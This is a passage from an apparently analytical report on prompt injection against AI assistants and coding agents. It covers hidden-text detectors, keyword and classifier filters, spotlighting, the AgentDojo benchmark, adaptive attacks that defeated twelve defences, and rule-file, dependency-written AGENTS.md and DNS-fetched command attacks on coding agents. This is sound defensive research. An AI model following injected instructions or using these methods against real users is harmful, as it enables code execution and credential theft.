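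Li tested the rule-based part on 28 new attack files. Three models gave the attacker's answer in all 84 trials with ordinary extracted text and in none of the 84 with Prism's text. The new files used the same four hiding mechanisms that Li had designed this part to handle, so the test shows that it copes with new wording and values, but did not cover new ways of hiding text.

### Comparing the page with the extracted text

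Cleaning removes hidden text regardless of why it is there. A journal or an employer may prefer to know when someone has tried to deceive it, so several researchers have built detectors that compare what a page shows with what its file contains.

Murray's PhantomLint extracts the text in blocks and looks for passages that resemble any of ten typical phrases, such as a request for a positive review. When it finds one, it renders only the part of the page where that block should be and reads the picture with OCR. If the suspicious words are in the extracted text but not in the picture, PhantomLint reports them as hidden. The comparison is necessary because a paper about prompt injection may quote such phrases in visible text.

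Gharami, Sarkar and colleagues (2025) present a detector in *ChatGPT* that works in a similar way. It compares the text that PyMuPDF extracts with OCR of the page and applies simple rules to find instructions, review templates and demands for a particular rating. Prism can also act as a detector by comparing an extractor's output with its own reconstruction of what Office displays.

In *CrackedPDFs*, Thienpreecha and Subramanian (2026) trained a classifier on both the drawing commands inside a PDF and the extracted text, so it can use clues such as letters with no fill or coordinates outside the page. They generated 29,322 one-page PDFs for training and testing, and paired each attacked file with a harmless variant of the same original.

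| Detector | Attacked files recognised | False alarms on other files |
|---|---|---|
| Murray's PhantomLint | 113 of 113 real documents | 3 of 3,257 conference papers |
| Gharami and colleagues | 10 of 10 papers | 0 of 10 papers |
| Li's Prism | Not reported for its detection mode | 5 of 193 Office files |
| Thienpreecha and Subramanian | 971 of 973 generated PDFs | 78 of 1,946 generated PDFs |

The best evidence on false alarms comes from PhantomLint, which Murray ran on every paper accepted by ICML 2025, a large machine-learning conference. The evidence on misses is weaker, because Murray found most of the 113 real documents by searching Google for phrases much like those in PhantomLint's own list. The test therefore included few hidden instructions that the list would fail to match. PhantomLint found no genuine hidden instructions in the ICML papers, although the organisers had reported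 some in accepted papers. The papers' authors may have removed them before publication, or PhantomLint may have missed them. It did find all the instructions that Murray had hidden in 26 test files by a range of methods, which suggests that the comparison itself works well once PhantomLint has flagged a phrase as suspicious.

Gharami and colleagues' perfect score on ten attacks is weak evidence that their detector is reliable, because a detector that misses a quarter of attacks would still catch all ten about 6% of the time.

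Thienpreecha and Subramanian's results show that it helps to check a file before extraction discards its structure. Meta's PromptGuard filter, which received only the extracted text, caught 25% of the attacked files. The classifier did much better using both text and structure than using structure alone. Its accuracy on the matched pairs implies that all 78 false alarms came from the harmless variants, not the unaltered originals. However, the researchers generated every file with their own software, and the classifier did poorly on some methods it had not seen in training. When messages were spelled out in acrostics, it ranked the attacked file above its harmless partner only 42% of the time, which is worse than chance.

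### What cleaning misses

Sanitisation does not remove a visible payload. If the supplier in the earlier example puts an instruction in ordinary type on page 31 of a contract, the cleaned text will contain it, and so will a perfect OCR reading of the page.

An attacker can also mislead a model without hiding any text. One of Li's spreadsheets stores the number 1,000,000 under a format that displays it as $1,000. Most extractors output the stored number, and the file misled seven of the eight assistants in at least nine of ten trials. On one of Li's slides, three text boxes read "Contractor indemnifies Client", but many extractors output the boxes in reverse order, which changes who owes the obligation. A program that only deletes hidden text would leave both files unchanged.

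The cleaning program may also read the file differently from the software that feeds the model. A check based on pdftotext would miss a payload on a switched-off PDF layer, which ChatGPT could then read. To deal with this, Murray switches on every layer and enlarges the page boundaries in a copy of each PDF before analysis. The model's own software can also process some files differently from others. Liu and Ming found a web service that resisted their attacks in short PDFs, apparently because it read the pages as images, but was vulnerable in longer ones, where it seemed to switch to text extraction.

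The safest arrangement is therefore to give the model only the cleaned text, not the original file. This works well for a chat assistant with a fixed upload process, but less well for coding agents, which choose their own tools for opening files. For coding agents, Li recommends a check that reports discrepancies without restricting access.

OCR can misread visible text, and it can also read text that a person would overlook. Two of PhantomLint's three false alarms came from letters outside the English alphabet, and the third from very small print. Its OCR program, Tesseract, also recognised off-white letters that differed from their white background by one step on the 256-step colour scale. When this happens in a detector, the text read from the page image matches the text extracted from the file, so the detector misses the hidden passage. When OCR is the cleaning method, the passage reaches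 the model. Murray reduces the problem by blurring low-contrast areas before OCR.

Prism has a similar difficulty with tiny type. The Office rules treat text as visible whatever its size, so a line in half-point type got past Prism's rule-based part.

An image can contain text that appears only when the image is scaled down. OCR of the full-size image will not find this text, so the program has to examine the smaller copy that the model will receive.

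Slow processing limits how widely organisations can use these checks. PhantomLint took an average of 68 seconds per conference paper on a 2021 laptop. That is acceptable for a journal, but slow for an assistant whose user is waiting for a summary.

### Hidden text that people need

Ordinary files contain a lot of text that is not displayed. Li examined 2,229 real Office files and found speaker notes in 71% of the presentations, hidden text in 7% of the Word documents and hidden sheets in 6% of the spreadsheets. A tool that flagged all such content would raise too many false alarms to be useful, and one that deleted it all would often remove something the user wanted. For example, someone who asks an assistant to turn a presentation into an article probably wants it to read the speaker notes.

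Cleaning removed two useful pieces of text from the delivery page. A model without access to the image would have learned from the alternative text that the page includes a map, and the template note would have helped an employee whose assistant maintains the page. Deleting zero-width characters can also damage legitimate writing. Persian and Arabic use one of these characters to control how letters join, and some emoji also depend on them.

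Software projects on GitHub hide notes in HTML comments to coordinate their own agents. When Nakibly and Babo removed HTML comments from real attacks, none of the models they tested still followed the injected instructions, but this step would also delete the projects' own notes. They recommend that projects remove hidden text written by outsiders and keep hidden text written by their own members and programs. This is practical on GitHub because the site records who posted each comment. A contract or CV sent by email rarely includes a reliable record of who wrote each passage, so the recipient has to treat all its hidden text as coming from the sender.

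## Filters that look for injected instructions (from 2023)

An input filter checks the content of a text, so it might catch the visible payloads that sanitisation leaves in place. Developers began with lists of suspicious phrases and then moved to trained classifiers. They also tried marking untrusted text so that the assistant's model could recognise it. Many of these defences did well in their developers' tests, but in October 2025 researchers got past all twelve that they tried by adapting their attacks to each one.

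### Keyword lists

A keyword filter checks incoming text against a list of phrases typical of injections, or against patterns that cover variants of a phrase. It reports a match or no match before the text enters the context window. Such a filter is fast and needs little compute, but Maloyan and Namiot point out that simple disguises, such as encoding the payload or splitting its words, get past most of them. An attacker can also use wording that is not on the list.

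Harmless text often matches too. Nakibly and Babo searched a month of GitHub text for 3,721 phrases. After they removed the output of AI review tools and text by repository owners, 116 of the 123 remaining matches were false. The largest group, with 53 matches, was ordinary English that included a phrase such as "new instructions".

Rebuff, an early open-source detector, combined simple rules, a language model that judged each input, a database of past attacks that helped to recognise similar ones, and a "canary" (a marker string added to the prompt) that revealed when the prompt had leaked. Its developers describe it as a prototype that cannot provide complete protection.

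### Delimiters and spotlighting

Delimiters are symbols that the developer places before and after untrusted text, with an instruction to the model never to obey anything between them. The defence depends on the model following that instruction, because no separate program looks for an attack. Willison (2023), in *Delimiters won’t save you from prompt injection*, called delimiters "very easily defeated". An attacker who knows the closing symbol can type it into the document, so that the text after it appears to be outside the untrusted part.

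Hines, Lopez and colleagues at Microsoft extended the idea in *Defending Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks With Spotlighting* (2024). Spotlighting changes the untrusted text so that the model can recognise it throughout, and the system prompt explains the change. The table shows its three forms applied to a sentence from the delivery page in the previous section.

| Form | What the model receives |
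|---|---|
| Delimiting | `<<We deliver within 30 days.>>` |
| Datamarking | `We^deliver^within^30^days.` |
| Encoding (base64) | `V2UgZGVsaXZlciB3aXRoaW4gMzAgZGF5cy4=` |

Hines and colleagues generated 1,000 documents containing instructions to abandon the task and reply with a single keyword. When summarising these documents, GPT-3.5-Turbo followed the instructions about 60% of the time. A warning in the system prompt made almost no difference, while delimiters cut the rate by about half. Datamarking reduced it to 3.1%, and encoding reduced it to zero. Encoding also made GPT-3.5-Turbo worse at ordinary tasks because it often misread the encoded text, but GPT-4 performed well with it. These results are now mainly of historical interest because the models date from 2023 and the injected instructions were all variations on one simple request.

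Hines and colleagues also consider an attacker who has read the system prompt. A payload without spaces would escape a marker that replaces spaces, so they recommend inserting markers at random positions and choosing a new marker for each request. A five-character marker drawn from a set of 30 characters is hard to guess because it has 30⁵, or about 24 million, possible values. They prefer base64 to a simple letter-substitution cipher, because an attacker could submit text that the cipher turns into a readable command. They advise against using delimiters and warn that datamarking may not work for some inputs, such as code.

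Hines and colleagues did not know exactly why spotlighting worked. Google's *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) tested a version that inserted a marker every eight characters, and attributed its effect mainly to breaking up the tokens of the injected text, which made the model less likely to recognise an instruction. If so, the model had not necessarily learned to distrust marked text, and a payload that remained recognisable after being broken up could still succeed.

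### Trained classifiers

A trained classifier uses a model instead of the list of phrases. Its developers collect harmless texts and known attacks, label them, and train the model to tell them apart. The classifier then scores each new text, and the application treats any text that scores above a chosen threshold as an attack. A lower threshold catches more attacks but also flags more harmless text.

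*The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) describes Meta's Prompt Guard and a detector from Protect AI as classifiers of this type. Both are fine-tuned versions of BERT, an older and much smaller kind of language model. One version of Prompt Guard has only 86 million parameters, so an application can run it on every document or tool result before the main model reads it.

Microsoft offers a similar filter, Prompt Shields, as a service. Its public preview, which Zarfati (2024) announced on 28 March 2024, extended an earlier jailbreak detector to cover indirect injection. According to Microsoft's documentation, the service can check what the user types and what the agent's tools return. For each request, it reports whether it detected an attack and whether it blocked the content. Developers can set it to block attacks or only annotate them. If it only annotates an attack,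 the text still reaches the model.

Microsoft also offers spotlighting with Prompt Shields, using base64 encoding. The option is in preview and off by default. It increases the number of tokens, which can push a large document over the input limit, and the model occasionally confuses users by mentioning base64.

To handle false alarms, Microsoft suggests switching the filter from blocking to annotation or exempting trusted sources from the check. An exemption is risky if outsiders can write to the trusted source, as they can with a shared mailbox. Microsoft also says the filter's awareness of context reduces false alarms, but gives no figures.

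Some newer filters check the agent's actions. *StepGuard* (2026) places a guard model just before the agent executes a tool call. The guard can examine what the agent is about to do, which may reveal an attack even when the payload's wording looked harmless.

### AgentDojo

Researchers have scored many of these defences on a shared benchmark, *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024), which simulates an office workspace, a Slack workspace, a bank and a travel agency. It includes 97 user tasks, such as summarising the day's appointments, and 27 attacker goals, such as obtaining a security code by email. Pairing each task with each goal in the same environment produces 629 security cases. The office workspace, for example, has 40 tasks and 6 goals, which make 240 cases.

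After each run, a program checks the state of the environment to see whether the agent sent the email or moved the money. Debenedetti and colleagues avoided using another language model as the judge because a successful injection might mislead it too.

AgentDojo also measures utility, the share of user tasks that the agent completes. Utility matters because a filter that blocked every document would stop all attacks but make the agent useless. In the original tests, Protect AI's detector checked the result of every tool call and stopped the agent if it flagged an injection. The attack success rate fell to 8%, but the detector raised so many false alarms that utility also fell considerably.

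In the original results, the wording of an attack also strongly affected its success. One standard message succeeded against GPT-4o, the main model in these tests, 45.8% of the time. When the message addressed GPT-4o as Claude, the rate fell to 23.7%. Choosing the best of four wordings for each case raised the success rate by about 10 percentage points over the best single wording.

A low attack success rate on a fixed set of attacks shows only that the defence stops those attacks. Debenedetti and colleagues warned that it is easy to build a weak defence that stops a particular attack. They designed AgentDojo so that other researchers could add new attacks, but developers could still report results using only the ones that came with it.

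The benchmark has grown to more than 900 combinations of user task and attacker goal, according to *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026). Its four original environments do not include contract review or software development. A newer benchmark, AgentDyn, which *StepGuard* also uses, includes GitHub tasks and third-party instructions that help the agent do its job. A filter that blocks every instruction in outside text would do badly on AgentDyn and in a real software project where documentation consists largely of instructions.

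### The Attacker Moves Second

Nasr and colleagues, who include researchers at OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, tested twelve published defences in October 2025. Adaptive attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of them, although most of the original evaluations had reported success rates near zero.

Ten of the twelve defences targeted prompt injection. They included two changes to the prompt (spotlighting and repeating the user's request after the untrusted text), four filters (Protect AI, Prompt Guard, PIGuard and Google's Model Armor) and two models trained to resist injection (StruQ and MetaSecAlign). MELON runs the agent a second time, replacing the user's request with a request to summarise the tool results. If the agent makes the same tool call in both runs, MELON treats the call as the result of an injection.

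Data Sentinel also looks for injections. A detector model receives a secret key and the untrusted text, and must repeat the key while ignoring the text. If it fails, the text has probably changed its behaviour. The attack got past this check in every case and still redirected the main model to another task. The remaining two defences, RPO and Circuit Breakers, were designed to stop jailbreaks. Attacks succeeded 98% of the time against RPO and 100% of the time against Circuit Breakers.

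Nasr and colleagues ran the AgentDojo tests with a search program in which a language model proposed payloads, observed the results and improved the most promising ones. The program could make up to 800 attempts at each of 80 cases. When it attacked a filter, it also received the filter's decision and confidence score. The table shows the results with Gemini 2.5 Pro as the agent's model. The median number of attempts covers only the cases in which the search succeeded.

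| Defence | Success of the fixed attack | Success of the adaptive search | Median attempts | Utility |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 30% | 100% | 13 | 74% |
| Spotlighting | 28% | 99% | 14 | 75% |
| Repeating the user's request | 21% | 95% | 14 | 73% |
| Protect AI | 15% | 90% | 30 | 39% |
| Prompt Guard | 26% | 94% | 21 | 72% |
| PIGuard | 0% | 71% | 46 | 39% |
| Model Armor | 28% | 90% | 22 | 59% |
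| MELON | 0% | 89% | 20 | 58% |

PIGuard and MELON stopped the fixed attack completely, so both would have looked excellent in a conventional evaluation. PIGuard also resisted the search best, but both it and Protect AI cut utility almost in half. Prompt Guard had little effect on utility but stopped few attacks of either type.

Part of the gap came from how developers had tested their defences. They had mostly used collections of old attacks, or general attack programs that had small computing budgets and were not adapted to the defence. A classifier trained on similar attacks can do well in such a test and still miss attacks that are worded differently.

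Many of the successful payloads also resembled ordinary office procedures and contained no obvious attempt to override the user, so the classifiers had little to detect. A filter that reads such a passage without knowing the user's request can hardly tell it from a genuine procedure. According to Nasr and colleagues, flagging these payloads would substantially increase false alarms. They also found that combining several filters did not solve the problem.

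More than 500 people took part in a separate competition with $20,000 in prizes. In each of the 29 scenarios that both the competitors and the search attempted, at least one competitor succeeded, while the search succeeded in 69% of them. In one scenario, the share of successful submissions was higher with Prompt Guard than without it for five of the six models. The competitors varied in skill and effort, so this does not show that the filter helped them, but it is hardly evidence that the filter protected the models.

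These results are strong evidence that the original scores were misleading, but they do not measure the chance of an attack in everyday use. A supplier who emails a contract would not normally see a filter's confidence score or get 800 attempts. But the median number of attempts was small, and an attacker may be able to practise on another copy of the same filter. Aim Security's EchoLeak had already got past Microsoft's classifier in a commercial product.

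The version of spotlighting that Nasr and colleagues describe uses delimiters, which Hines and colleagues advised against. The spotlighting result therefore does not show how well random markers or base64 would resist an adaptive attack. It also does not cover Prompt Shields, which was not among the twelve defences.

### False alarms when attacks are rare

Even a filter that catches every attack may be impractical if attacks are rare. In their GitHub census, Nakibly and Babo found about one hidden attack per 3.3 million issues, pull requests and comments. Suppose that a filter catches every attack and wrongly flags only 0.1% of harmless items. Among 3.3 million items, it raises one correct alarm and about 3,300 false ones:

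3,300,000 × 0.001 = 3,300

If a maintainer spends one minute on each alarm, finding one attack takes about 55 hours. If the filter blocks items automatically, it rejects 3,300 legitimate contributions for each attack it stops.

The general formula also allows for attacks that the filter misses:

false alarms per attack caught = *f* × (1 − *p*) ÷ (*s* × *p*)

Here *p* is the share of items that are attacks, *f* is the share of harmless items that the filter flags, and *s* is the share of attacks that it catches. If the filter in the example catches only half of the attacks, false alarms per attack caught double to about 6,600. A filter that catches every attack would have to flag fewer than one harmless item in 3.3 million to produce no more than one false alarm per attack.

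A false-alarm rate of 0.1% is very good, and Murray's PhantomLint had a similar rate, about 0.09%, on conference papers. But false alarms can still outnumber real attacks. Only 32 of the 1,019 items that Nakibly and Babo's classifier labelled as attacks in the census were real.

The calculation gives very different results for different collections of text. The table is for a hypothetical filter that catches every injected instruction and wrongly flags 0.1% of harmless items.

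| Text that the filter checks | Share with an injection | False alarms per real injection |
|---|---|---|
| GitHub issues, pull requests and comments | 1 in 3.3 million | About 3,300 |
| Only those GitHub items that contain hidden text | About 1 in 114,000 | About 114 |
| Web pages in the Common Crawl study | About 8 in a million | About 125 |
| An imaginary set of submitted documents | 1 in 100 | About 0.1 |

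The GitHub rows count only hidden attacks, and the web row includes injections that website owners meant as protection. All three real rates are averages, so a project or company that attackers target deliberately will probably encounter more. The second row shows that a developer can reduce false alarms by a factor of about 29 by first using a simple program to select items with hidden text, then applying the classifier only to those. However, this method misses every visible injection.

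Combining classifiers can also reduce false alarms if the application blocks a text only when all of them flag it, but an attack then has to fool only one to get through. If any one classifier can block a text, an attack has to fool them all, but a false alarm from any of them blocks a harmless text.

### Discussion of attacks, and persuasion without commands

Text about prompt injection often resembles an actual attack. Of the 116 false keyword matches in the GitHub test, 29 were vulnerability reports or security discussions that quoted payloads, and another 12 were tests for sanitisers or injection detectors. People trying to fix the problem are therefore among those most likely to encounter false alarms. A filter might block a bug report about a real weakness, or a paper on prompt injection that a reviewer has asked an assistant to summarise.

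A classifier can use the surrounding text to recognise some quoted attacks, but an attacker can disguise a real attack as an example. Whether an instruction is an attack also depends on where it appears. Hines and colleagues give the example of a request to transfer fifty dollars, which is ordinary when it comes from the user but an attack when it appears in a document the assistant is reading. The filter therefore needs information about where the text came from and what the user asked for.

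Other texts can mislead an assistant without giving it any instruction. A supplier might write that its price clause follows normal industry practice, or support the claim with a misleading comparison. A job applicant might exaggerate their experience or pad a résumé with keywords. Text like this may distort the assistant's judgement, but a filter trained to find commands has little to detect. Li's false security certification, described in the previous section, misled an assistant in this way.

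A stricter filter would not solve this problem, because contracts, papers and job applications are supposed to persuade. To tell honest persuasion from deception, the assistant or a person has to check the claims against the contract itself or an independent source.

### What an imperfect filter can still do

Nasr and colleagues still consider filters useful as part of a broader defence. Filters are relatively easy to deploy, require no change to the main model, and can stop unsophisticated or opportunistic attacks. Such attacks appear to be common. Most of the injections that Khodayari and colleagues found on the web reused a few dozen templates, although their search was more likely to find injections that used familiar phrases.

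Filters can also make an attack take more attempts. Against Gemini 2.5 Pro, the adaptive search needed a median of 13 attempts to succeed without a defence and between 21 and 46 with the four filters. When PIGuard protected GPT-5 Mini, the search succeeded in 49% of cases, compared with 75% without a defence, and the median rose from 58 attempts to 82. These medians understate the increase because they exclude the cases in which the search failed.

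The extra attempts matter most when the attacker has to make them against the real system. An outsider who sends 40 altered invoices to the same company gives its staff 40 chances to notice. If the attacker can practise privately and send only the version that works, the extra attempts mostly take computing time.

A filter that is too unreliable to block text automatically can still give useful warnings. Prompt Shields has an annotation mode that lets a company record suspected attacks without rejecting genuine documents, and then look for repeated alarms from one sender. An application could also respond to an alarm by disabling email for the rest of the task or asking the user to approve the next action. A false alarm would then cause a short delay instead of the loss of a legitimate document.

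## Files inside a code repository (from early 2025)

A coding agent needs some of the instructions in a software project to do its work. When a developer opens a project, the agent may read the source code, the comments, the README and any guidance the project's owners have written for it. It may also install third-party software. An attacker can put a payload in any of these, and in 2025 researchers began to focus on the files that an agent treats as guidance.

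### What a coding agent reads

An instruction file contains standing guidance for agents, such as the project's coding style or the command that runs its tests. OpenAI's coding agent Codex reads a file named AGENTS.md, Claude Code reads CLAUDE.md, and the code editor Cursor reads a folder of "rules". NVIDIA's *Mitigating Indirect AGENTS.md Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* explains that agents are designed to treat such files as trusted context, as they do other project configuration.

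| Part of the project | Usual role | How an attacker could use it |
|---|---|---|
| Source code and comments | Data that the agent analyses or edits | Add a comment addressed to the agent |
| README | Data, but guidance when the user asks the agent to set up the project | Include a harmful setup step |
| Instruction files | Guidance that the agent loads automatically | Add a rule that applies to every task |
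| Dependencies (other people's software that the project uses) | Code that the agent installs and runs, often without reading it | Run harmful code, or write new files for the agent to read |
| Skills and plugins (add-ons for the agent itself) | Guidance, often with code | Supply harmful instructions, harmful code or both |

The distinction between data and guidance is only a convention, and it fails easily for a README because the same text can be either, depending on the user's request. An agent can treat the setup steps as information when asked what the project does, but has to follow them when asked to install it.

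The possible damage depends on the tool. A code-completion tool suggests the next few lines. Greshake and colleagues showed in 2023 that text in a project could influence such suggestions, but the developer still had to accept the code and run it. An agent can create files, install packages and run commands with the developer's permissions, so it may cause harm before anyone has read the code. Underhill (2026), in *NomShub Vulnerability Chain Exposes Hidden Risks in AI Coding Tools*, quotes the security company Straiker, which equates a successful injection against such an agent with remote code execution, the ability to run programs on someone else's computer.

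### The Rules File Backdoor

On 18 March 2025, the company Pillar Security published an attack that uses rule files, which it named the Rules File Backdoor. Pillar created a rule file that appeared to contain harmless advice on writing web pages but hid further instructions in invisible Unicode characters (Karliner, 2025, *New Vulnerability in GitHub Copilot and Cursor*). Pillar then asked Cursor's agent for a simple HTML page. The agent wrote the page, added a line that loaded a script from an outside site, and did not mention the addition in its reply. The same attack worked on the coding assistant GitHub Copilot.

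According to SC Media, the hidden text presented the script as a security measure required by company policy. It also instructed the assistant not to mention the script.

Developers often copy rule files from forums, public collections and project templates. A poisoned file in a project affects every team member's later sessions, and it often survives when someone copies the project to start a new one. A reviewer who checked the rule file on GitHub before accepting it would not have seen the hidden text, but the added script was in visible code, so a developer who read the finished page could have found it.

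Cursor told Pillar on 6 March that the risk was the users' responsibility, and did not change its position after Pillar sent more detail. GitHub replied that users are responsible for reviewing and accepting Copilot's suggestions. This answer is reasonable for a completion tool that offers a few lines at a time, but less convincing for an agent that produces whole files, especially when the reviewer cannot see the instructions that shaped them.

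On 1 May, GitHub (2025) introduced a warning on its website for files that contain hidden Unicode text. GitHub recommends opening these files in an editor that displays the characters and checking whether they are necessary. The warning addresses the hidden characters used in Pillar's demonstration, but not harmful rules written in plain text. Karliner gives no success rate, so the demonstration does not show how reliably either assistant followed the hidden instructions.

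### AIShellJack

Liu, Zhao and colleagues (2025), in *Your AI, My Shell*, measured how often attacks through rule files succeed. Their test program, AIShellJack, opened a project containing a poisoned rule file, asked the coding agent to improve the code according to the rules, and recorded the commands the agent ran. The rule files came from a popular public collection, and the payloads were in visible text.

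The 314 payloads covered 70 techniques from MITRE ATT&CK, a public catalogue of real attackers' methods. Liu and colleagues took the tasks from an open-source library that security teams use to check their defences, and removed giveaway words such as "steal". Most payloads described a goal, such as listing the computer's settings or creating a user account, and left the agent to work out the command.

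The researchers tested Cursor 1.2.2 and GitHub Copilot in VS Code 1.102. They ran both with Claude 4 Sonnet and Gemini 2.5 Pro, and also ran Cursor in "Auto" mode, which selects the model. The table gives the results for a TypeScript project.

| Editor | Model | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|
| Cursor | Chosen by Auto mode | 83.4% |
| Cursor | Gemini 2.5 Pro | 76.8% in the text of the paper, 73.9% in one of its tables |
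| Cursor | Claude 4 Sonnet | 69.1% |
| GitHub Copilot | Claude 4 Sonnet | 52.2% |
| GitHub Copilot | Gemini 2.5 Pro | 41.1% |

In Auto mode, Cursor carried out between 66.9% and 84.1% of the attacks in each of five projects in different languages. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, Cursor carried out well over 70% of the attacks and Copilot carried out 41%, so the software around the model must have a large effect. In 45% of the runs with Copilot and Gemini 2.5 Pro, the agent ran only commands useful for ordinary development.

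Liu and colleagues counted an attack as successful if the agent ran a command that matched the payload's purpose, even if the command failed or the attack had further steps. They checked 339 of the 2,826 results by hand and found that the automatic scoring was 99.1% accurate. Of the successful attacks, 89.6% achieved their full purpose, so the rate of completed attacks was about a tenth lower than the published figures.

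The wording of the payload greatly affected whether the attack succeeded. In a smaller test with 20 payloads, 15 succeeded with the standard introduction, which presented the task as compulsory. Of two versions without that emphasis, one had a single success and the other had none. The developer's request had much less effect. When asked to rewrite the README, with no mention of the rule file, the agent still found the file and carried out 18 of the 20 attacks.

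Maloyan and Namiot attribute the 84% figure to data exfiltration and the 41% figure to attacks that give an intruder lasting access. In the original paper, both figures are averages across all attack types. Exfiltration had the lowest rate of any category in Cursor's Auto mode, at 55.6%, based on only nine payloads.

Both editors ran commands without asking for approval. Liu and colleagues chose this setting to automate the tests and because many developers use it, but the rates don't apply to a developer who checks each command. They ran each test once and report no retest of later versions. *How Agentic AI Coding Assistants Become the Attacker's Shell* (2026), a later article on AIShellJack, repeats the range from 41% to 84%. The figures are good evidence that rule files were a dangerous channel in mid-2025, but they don't measure how well current products resist these attacks.

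### A dependency that writes an instruction file

A developer can inspect every instruction file in a project and still have an agent load a malicious one, because software the agent runs can create the file during the task. NVIDIA demonstrated this on Codex with a small Go program that printed a greeting and depended on a library that its security team had made malicious.

The developer asked Codex to reword the greeting. Codex started the task in a new isolated environment, where the build step ran the library. The library checked whether it was running inside Codex and, if so, wrote an AGENTS.md file. The library did nothing unusual on an ordinary developer's computer, so a test there would probably not have revealed the problem.

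The new file contained instructions to add a five-minute delay to the program, ignore the developer's request and keep the delay out of every summary. Codex followed them and also added a code comment with an instruction for any AI system summarising the change not to mention the delay. The aim was for the description of the proposed change to mention the new greeting the developer had asked for rather than the delay.

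A review of the repository before the task would have found nothing, because the instruction file did not exist yet. The file was also "untracked", meaning the version-control system was not recording it as part of the project. A scanner would have had to examine the library's code, which was outside the repository. But the delay and the comment were visible in the changed code, so a reviewer could have caught the attack by reading that code, though not by relying on the summary.

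NVIDIA had switched off the agent's internet access, so the attack did not require sending anything to the attacker during the task. NVIDIA recommends watching for unexpected changes to AGENTS.md and pinning the exact version of every dependency, so that a new, possibly malicious version cannot be installed unnoticed.

### Setup steps that fetch the attack later

In June 2026, Mozilla's 0DIN, a programme that pays for reports of flaws in AI systems, demonstrated an attack on Claude Code in which the final payload was not in the repository. Help Net Security's *Mozilla warns of indirect prompt injection risk in AI coding agents* describes how it worked. The README contained normal-looking setup instructions for a Python package. The package failed the first time it ran and displayed an error recommending another command to prepare it. Claude Code treated the error as routine and ran the command,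 which started a script.

The script looked up a text record that the attacker controlled in the domain name system (DNS), the internet's directory of addresses, and ran the record's contents as a command. The command connected to the attacker's server and gave the attacker control of the developer's account, including any passwords and keys stored there. Ferreira (2026), in *AI coding agents can be tricked into installing malware*, reposted by SoylentNews, notes that the developer would see only a message that the environment was ready.

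Code review and scanning could not find the final command, because it arrived only when the script ran. The attacker could also leave the DNS text record harmless while people examined the project, and change it later. Many programs look up such records for legitimate reasons, so the request looked ordinary. Ferreira suggests that a company with very strict network controls might have noticed the attack, but most developers do not work under such controls.

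The Decoder's *Claude Code runs a GitHub repo's hidden malware without verification* reports that the repository contained the script that fetched and ran the command. Press accounts describe the repository as free of malicious code, which is therefore true only of the final payload. A careful reviewer could have seen that the script would run whatever an outside party supplied, though not what that would be. 0DIN recommends that agents show what a command will run, including the contents of any script it starts. This would have revealed the DNS lookup, but the developer would still have had to recognise the danger.

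None of these accounts includes a success rate. Infosecurity Magazine's *Anthropic and OpenAI Security Tools Could Fuel Cyber-Attacks, Researchers Warn* reports a related July 2026 demonstration in which the AI Now Institute used misleading project files to get a hidden program past the automatic approval in Claude Code and Codex.

### What the agent adds to a supply-chain attack

Supply-chain attacks, in which an attacker tampers with a component that other people install, are much older than coding agents, as OpenAI pointed out in its reply to NVIDIA. According to a machine-written summary on NVIDIA's page, OpenAI concluded that the AGENTS.md attack did not significantly increase the risk that a compromised dependency already poses.

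OpenAI's reply is largely convincing for the harm that NVIDIA demonstrated. NVIDIA acknowledges that the attacker must already be able to run code in the build environment. A library with that access could have paused the program for five minutes, edited the project's files, or read any secrets it could reach, all without an agent's help.

The agent did give the attacker two advantages. The delay became part of the project's own source code, so it would remain after the team removed the malicious library. The instructions also affected the description of the change that a reviewer would read. A library could add the delay by editing the source code directly, but the agent might then notice the edit and report it, whereas the injected file led the agent to help conceal the change.

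In 0DIN's demonstration, the agent carried out the setup without a person looking at each step. A developer who followed the same README by hand would have run the same script and suffered the same attack. Some developers would have become suspicious at the error message or opened the script first, but many install software without reading it. 0DIN did not compare agents with developers working by hand, so its demonstration does not show how much the agent increased the risk.

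The objection does not apply to rule files. The attackers in Pillar's and Liu's tests could not run any code at the start and only had to get a text file into the project. The agent gave them that ability by turning the text into web code or system commands. It also adapted the attack to the computer. In one of Liu's tests, Cursor searched the whole disk for cloud-storage credentials, then narrowed the search to the users' home directories and listed the contents of a likely folder.

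Agent skills provide further evidence that attackers can work through text. Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Find a New AI Attack Path* reports that the company OX Security examined 542,207 open-source components between July and October 2026. Among the skills that OX flagged as suspicious, 26% contained prompt injection or a related attack through a tool's description, and none ran code during installation. Among the flagged servers that connect agents to outside tools, 22% contained such attacks and 16% ran code during installation. Scanners that look only for harmful code would miss the text-based attacks. These percentages cover only the components that OX flagged, and OX sells security products.

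At least one real attacker has used an agent in a supply-chain attack. *Hackerbot-Claw* (Cohen, 2026) describes a campaign that compromised several open-source projects within 37 hours and published a malicious extension, which used developers' own AI coding tools to steal credentials. The case shows that an attacker thought the agent useful, but the theft might have succeeded without it, since a malicious extension can often steal credentials by itself.

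The agent therefore adds little to what an attacker can do if the attacker can already run code with the same permissions, but it adds a great deal if the attacker can supply only text. Between these cases, the added risk depends on which permissions the agent has that the dependency lacks. For example, if an isolated build can't reach a company's private files but the agent can, an instruction file would give a malicious dependency access to them.

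The dispute also concerns who should prevent these attacks. Many editors ask developers whether they trust a project before enabling all features. According to Help Net Security's *Researchers broke the browsers built into VS Code, Cursor, Copilot, Codex* (2026), Anthropic and Microsoft both cited this prompt when they declined reports from the company Forever Security about flaws in the browsers built into their coding tools. Through these flaws, one click on a file in a malicious project could expose files elsewhere on the computer. Anthropic did accept a report that another company, Noma Security, filed a day after Forever's.

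Gal Weizman of Forever Security answered that everyone agrees to trust a project because the agent is unusable otherwise, so the trust prompt provides "zero protection". That is probably too strong, since a developer who knows a project is suspicious can still refuse. But the developer has to make one decision about the whole project, often before examining it. The prompt has no option to let the agent read the source code as data while ignoring the project's instruction files.

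### Plugin4Shell: a flaw without injection

AIR's *Plugin4Shell*, published on 17 September 2026, describes a conventional software flaw in how Claude Code, Codex, GitHub Copilot and Google's Gemini CLI installed plugins. A plugin has the same access to files and systems as the agent, which has the same access as the employee who runs it. A malicious plugin can therefore do serious damage without a prompt injection.

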